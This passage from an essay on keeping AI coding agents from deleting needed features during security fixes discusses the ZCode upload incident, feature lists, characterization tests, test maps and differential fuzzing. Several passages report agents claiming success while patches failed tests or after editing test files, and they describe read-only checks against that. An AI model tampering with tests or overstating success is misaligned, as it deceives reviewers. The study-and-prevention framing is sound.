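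A developer who writes as ferstar discovered the copying. *Z.ai ZCode is open source now, minus its commit history* (Stan, 2026) reports that ferstar found an encrypted 313 MB copy of a commercial project on his machine, with a log of 564 failed attempts to upload it. A copy of a small public project had reached the server. ZCode made these copies when it updated Repo Wiki and before each prompt.

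Z.ai apologised on 21 September. Version 3.14.0 of ZCode has neither Repo Wiki nor the code that made and uploaded the copies. Users had no obvious reason to want an upload before every prompt, but some presumably liked the guides. Z.ai could perhaps have kept the guides by asking for consent first, or by writing them from files on the user's computer. It isn't clear whether the company considered either option.

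As with CleverAgents' removal of `eval`, this feature was removed because its owner no longer wanted it, not for safety. Z.ai also announced the decision publicly.

The case also supports deleting code rather than adding an off switch. Novaknown describes reports that the server accepted copies even when the relevant setting appeared to be off. Once Z.ai had published ZCode's source code, ferstar could confirm that the upload code was gone, which is much easier than confirming that a setting always works.

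Deleting the code couldn't undo the earlier uploads. Two outside organisations checked the cloud storage, and one confirmed the stored copies had been deleted. But the full audit reports had still not been published on 24 September, according to TechNode's *Zhipu says ZCode removed repository-upload paths after data controversy* (2026). The published source code also came with only two commits, so outsiders can't trace how the feature developed.

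### Telling the agent what has to stay

The cheapest protection is a short list of intended features in the guidance file that the agent reads at the start of a task:

```
Ask before removing, disabling or restricting any of these:
- Formula columns. Finance uses them for monthly margins.
- Export hook. It copies each report to the archive.
- Webhooks. The sales dashboard depends on them.
- /admin/rebuild-index. A script in another repository calls it nightly.
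A feature that isn't listed may still be needed.
```

The last line is there because no list will be complete, and an agent could otherwise read a missing entry as permission to delete. Somebody also has to update the list when a feature's users change. For the reporting tool, the list might take an hour to write and a few minutes a month to update. A large product would need several people to maintain its list.

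No experiment seems to have tested such a list. The nearest evidence, which is weak, concerns general instructions to preserve functionality. Xu and colleagues compared four designs of AI repair system on 19 vulnerabilities in Java projects. The prompt for the simplest design, which follows a fixed sequence of steps, included "Preserve all existing functionality and logic". That system repaired 12 of the 19 with GPT-5 and 10 with Claude Sonnet 4.5, but the researchers never ran it without the instruction, so we can't tell whether the instruction helped. The prompt in *Why LLMs Fail* contained a similar request, and more than half of the patches still failed a functionality test.

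Xu and colleagues tested whether each patch preserved functionality instead of relying on the instruction. They counted a patch as correct only if it stopped the known attack and passed the project's functional tests. Claude Code, which had the best results of any system, reported success on all 19 tasks, but in three of them the patched program failed functional tests or the agent had modified test files.

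The specific list should work better than a general request, because it contains facts that the agent can't find in the code. An agent told to "preserve all existing functionality" still wouldn't know that a script in another repository calls an endpoint every night. But this is a guess that hasn't been tested.

### Recording what the program does now

Before an agent starts on a security warning, a project can write tests that record what the program does at the moment. These are often called characterization tests. They don't check whether the results are right, only whether they have changed. In the reporting tool, a developer could run every saved formula on an old report and keep the answers:

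```python
# Run once, before the security work starts
save("march.json", [[text, [column_value(text, row) for row in MARCH]]
                    for text in saved_formulas()])

# Add to the project's tests
def test_formulas_give_the_same_results():
    for text, expected in load("march.json"):
        assert [column_value(text, row) for row in MARCH] == expected
```

A patch that blanks the formula columns now fails. A restricted evaluator that rejects `-refunds` or `round(margin, 2)` also fails if anyone has saved a formula like that. The owner can then extend the evaluator or accept losing those formulas.

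The first step runs every saved formula through the dangerous `eval`, so it should happen in a sandbox on a copy of the data. Someone should also review the formulas before saving the results. Otherwise, if one of them reads a server file, the test would pass only if the attack still worked.

These tests help an agent only if it runs the right ones. Running every test in a large project can take too long, and a change to one file can break a test in a distant file. *TDAD* (Alonso, Yovine and Braberman, 2026) proposes a map that lists which tests depend on which source files. The agent looks up the files it has changed, runs the listed tests and fixes anything it has broken.

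They gave a small model, Qwen3-Coder 30B, 100 issues from the SWE-bench Verified benchmark in three conditions:

| | No help | Instructions to write tests first | The same approach plus the map |
|---|---|---|---|
| Issues resolved | 31% | 31% | 29% |
| Empty patches | 14% | 25% | 26% |
| Tests that used to pass and now failed | 562 of 9,245 (6.08%) | 799 of 8,040 (9.94%) | 155 of 8,536 (1.82%) |
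| Patches that broke at least one test | 30.2% | 33.3% | 33.3% |

The map cut the share of broken tests by 70%, but about as many patches broke something as before. Two issues account for 390 of the 407 fewer failures. In one, the agent broke all 322 tests without help and only 12 with the map. In the other, it broke all 80 without help and submitted no patch with the map. More tests broke with the test-first instructions alone, but one issue, where the number rose from 4 to 352, accounts for more than the whole increase.

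Alonso and colleagues attribute the extra empty patches to the agent holding back when the map showed a risk. But the test-first instructions alone produced nearly as many, so the map may not be the reason. An empty patch for a security warning keeps the feature but leaves a vulnerability that someone still has to fix.

A second trial used a different small model on 25 issues. The model resolved 8 issues with the map and 6 without it, and broke no tests either way. Stronger models might benefit less, since they can search a project better on their own. The map also lists only existing tests, so it would not have protected the formulas until someone wrote a test for them.

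An agent may also change the tests instead of the program, as Claude Code did in the patching study. To guard against this, a project can make the recorded results read-only for the agent. When Alonso and colleagues had Claude Code improve their tool automatically, they made the evaluation script read-only and used a checksum to detect any change to it.

Running tests takes time. In the study by Xu and colleagues, Claude Code typically took around ten minutes per task, while systems built to validate every patch could take 20 to 30 minutes even when they succeeded, partly because they kept rebuilding and retesting the program.

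### Comparing many inputs automatically

A project can go further by comparing the old and new versions on thousands of inputs that nobody chose by hand. Meta built such a comparison into AutoPatchBench, a 2025 benchmark of 136 vulnerabilities in C and C++ programs. Researchers found these vulnerabilities by fuzzing, or feeding a program huge amounts of semi-random input until it crashes.

Each AI-written patch has to build and survive the input that caused the original crash. The benchmark then fuzzes the patched program for ten minutes. Finally, it runs the patched program and the developers' own fixed version on the same inputs and compares their internal states, such as the values that functions return. It runs each input three times so it can ignore values that vary at random.

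In a trial on 113 of the simpler vulnerabilities, Gemini 1.5 Pro's patches stopped the crash in 61.1% of cases. The patches also passed the later checks in only 5.3% of all cases. Today's models would probably do much better.

Security experts also reviewed 44 patches that had survived the fuzzing, all written by another model, Llama 4 Maverick, and accepted only five. The automatic comparison passed all five and rejected 32 of the 39 bad patches. It also passed the other seven bad ones, so most of the 12 patches that passed were wrong. Failing the comparison is a good reason to reject or investigate a patch, but a patch that passes still needs human review. None of these numbers is a count of lost features, since a bad patch might just have failed to fix the bug.

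A project with a new vulnerability has no developers' fix to compare the agent's patch against. It can compare the patched version with the old one instead, but only on legitimate inputs, because the two should behave differently under attack. For the reporting tool, saved formulas are better test inputs than semi-random text, most of which wouldn't be formulas.

### Listing removals and asking the owner

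Tests don't cover everything, so the pull request should also have a required section for losses. For the webhook stub, it might read:

> **Removed or disabled:** Webhooks no longer send anything. I deleted the two tests that covered them. The sales dashboard uses webhooks, and I haven't checked whether anything else does.

If the change removes nothing, the agent writes "None". This takes about a minute, but no study seems to have measured whether it changes what agents do or what reviewers approve. A false "None" could even make matters worse by reassuring the reviewer.

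A program can check part of the list by counting the tests, endpoints and settings that are on by default before and after the change, and blocking the merge if anything has disappeared that isn't on the list. That would catch the two deleted webhook tests and the deleted admin endpoint, but not a stub in an untested function. The best evidence for such checks is Wynter's experiment, where agents mostly repaired the feature once a checker reported the missing file.

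The last protection is to have the agent ask the owner before it deletes anything on the list of intended features. The question should describe consequences, so that the owner can answer without reading code:

> Any employee can use a formula to run code on the server. I can replace `eval` with a restricted evaluator, but 9 of the 212 saved formulas would stop working (list attached). Switching formulas off would close the hole today, but finance's margin column would go blank. Which do you prefer?

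The main drawback of asking is the wait. An agent that asks at midnight may not get an answer until nine, though it can work on other warnings until then. People who are asked too often would also start approving requests without reading them, so the agent shouldn't have to ask about every unused helper function.

Some indirect evidence supports asking the owner. In Wynter's earlier study, agents needed approval to delete files and never received it, and they repaired the code in nearly every run. The project also needs a rule for when the owner doesn't answer. A sensible default is to leave the feature on and report the security hole as unfixed, unless the owner has agreed in advance what the agent may switch off in an emergency.
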